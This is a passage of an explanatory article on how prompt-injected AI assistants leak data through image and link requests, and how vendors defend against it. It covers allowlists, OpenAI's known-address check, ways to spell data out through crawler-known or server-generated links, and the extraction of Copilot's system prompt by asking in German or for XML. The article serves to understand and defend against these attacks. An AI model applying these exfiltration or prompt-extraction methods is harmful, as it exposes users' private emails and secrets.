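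A permitted site can also be dangerous if it stores what people send it. The CSP for the AI assistant in Superhuman, an email application, allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms is on the same domain and saves data sent in an ordinary image request. In January 2026 Willison described how a malicious email made the assistant send the contents of dozens of other emails to an attacker's form. Superhuman treated the problem as urgent and fixed it.

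Even when a permitted site belongs to a company that won't steal the data itself, such as Google or Microsoft, the developer has to know whether any page on the site will fetch another address, save what it receives or let strangers publish. That is almost impossible to check for a domain as large as Bing's. An allowlist is much safer when it contains only a server that the vendor uses for its own pictures.

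### Loading only addresses that are already public

OpenAI avoids this problem by checking the whole address instead of the site. ChatGPT automatically loads an address only if OpenAI's crawler has already recorded it.

Such a check should have stopped SearchLeak's image request if Copilot had used it. The request went to Bing's public site, but its address contained the title of a private email, so the crawler wouldn't have recorded that address and the browser wouldn't have loaded it. Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red's account of his DEF CON talk in 2026 that Google used its search index in a similar way, and that he didn't think Copilot had this protection yet.

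The check makes bulk theft impractical because an attacker can no longer put new text into an address and can only choose from addresses the crawler already knows. If they spell data out, as Rehberger did in 2023, each request reveals one character. A 2,000-character email would take about 2,000 requests, while an ordinary image leak could send it in one or a few.

Browsers make even that difficult because they often keep a copy of a picture and don't request it twice. "Bluebell Barn" has 12 letters but only seven different ones, so the attacker might see requests for b, l, u, e, a, r and n, possibly in the wrong order. Rehberger, discussing OpenAI's paper on Embrace The Red, suggests enforcing this limit by storing each response for a few minutes or refusing to visit the same address twice in a session.

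An attacker could get around such a rule by using a different address for each letter in each position. A 12-letter name would take 312 addresses, and the crawler would have to find them all beforehand. Rehberger points out that an attacker could also prepare thousands of addresses and tell the model what each one means. With 1,000 addresses, one request could represent any three digits, so two requests would be enough for a six-digit login code. The check therefore protects long emails and files well, but short secrets less well.

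It also protects users only if the attacker can't control the list of known addresses. Anthropic used a different rule for Claude's web-reading tool, which accepted an address only if the user had typed it, a web search had returned it, or a page Claude had already read linked to it. Paul (2026) got around this in *The Memory Heist* by making a website with a link for every letter. The first page linked to `/a`, `/b` and so on, `/a` linked to `/aa` and `/ab`, and the server created each new page when Claude asked for it. Claude spelled out Paul's name by following one link after another.

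Every link in that attack came from a page Claude had read, so the rule allowed it. OpenAI's check would be much harder to defeat this way. There are nearly 12 million five-letter combinations, and the crawler would need to have recorded the right one before the attack.

Many harmless addresses fail the check. A new page, or a picture behind a company login, may not be in the index. ChatGPT shows the user the address and warns that it may contain information from the conversation. This helps against one-click attacks such as Logue's login button, but the user can still choose to continue. When OpenAI explained why it didn't use a strict list of sites, it said that frequent warnings can train people to click through them.

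Developers also have to use the check everywhere. OpenAI's first version was missing from its iPhone and Mac applications, and Rehberger thinks the same could happen with the new one because some developers at the company may not know about it. A diagram renderer that loads images without calling the checking service would be as exposed as before.

### Controlling requests or training the model

Because prompt injection has no certain fix, Rehberger advises companies to assume that an attack on the model will succeed and to limit the damage by controlling what the assistant can do. He also worries that people become less careful as models improve and start treating the model as a security barrier.

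Rehberger's own experience with Copilot supports his view. Microsoft had tried to stop Copilot from revealing its system prompt, the developer's instructions to the model, but he got Copilot to print it in German instead of English. Microsoft later blocked that too. When Copilot also refused to list its tools, he asked it to put their names into an XML document, and it did. Microsoft's protections against prompt injection also failed to block any of the three ReLeak attacks. Cato's researchers used AI agents to study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt. As agents make it easier to try many wordings, a defence that works most of the time becomes less useful.

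*The Framing Gap (2026)* tested whether hostile text could make AI agents reveal a secret they had been told to protect. The order to protect it did little to help. Attacks that presented the malicious instruction as part of the task succeeded in 31.9% of trials with the order and 38.1% without it, a difference small enough to be chance.

In the same paper's tests, ChatGPT as an ordinary product did not leak the secret in any of 48 valid trials, while the model that developers use directly leaked it in up to 100% of trials. The researchers couldn't tell whether the model or some other part of the product prevented the leaks. The 48 trials also don't prove that the product is safe. An attack that worked 6% of the time would still have about a 5% chance of failing in all 48, and an attacker who can email thousands of people doesn't need a high success rate.

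A good reply to Rehberger is that vendors have a poor record of controlling requests too. They have to find every way out because an attacker needs only one. ReLeak used images, saved files and a code interpreter that, according to Microsoft's documentation, had no network access. A model that ignored the malicious email would have stopped all three attacks, as well as any that nobody has discovered yet. Blocking requests also doesn't stop a hijacked assistant from giving the user a false summary or deleting a file, since it can do either without contacting an outside server.

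Google and OpenAI accept this reply insofar as they use both approaches. Google continues to train its models to resist injections, and OpenAI calls its address check one layer among several. Rehberger doesn't object to training. The disagreement is about which defence a company should rely on when the other fails.

Rehberger is right about diagrams. A flowchart doesn't need anything from another server, so the developer can block every request without working out which ones are dangerous. Training matters more for an assistant that sends emails or browses the web, because it has to contact other people's servers to be useful and no simple rule separates a legitimate message from a theft. But if that training fails, an attacker can get everything the model can read, whereas one who gets past a check like OpenAI's may have to collect the data a few characters at a time.
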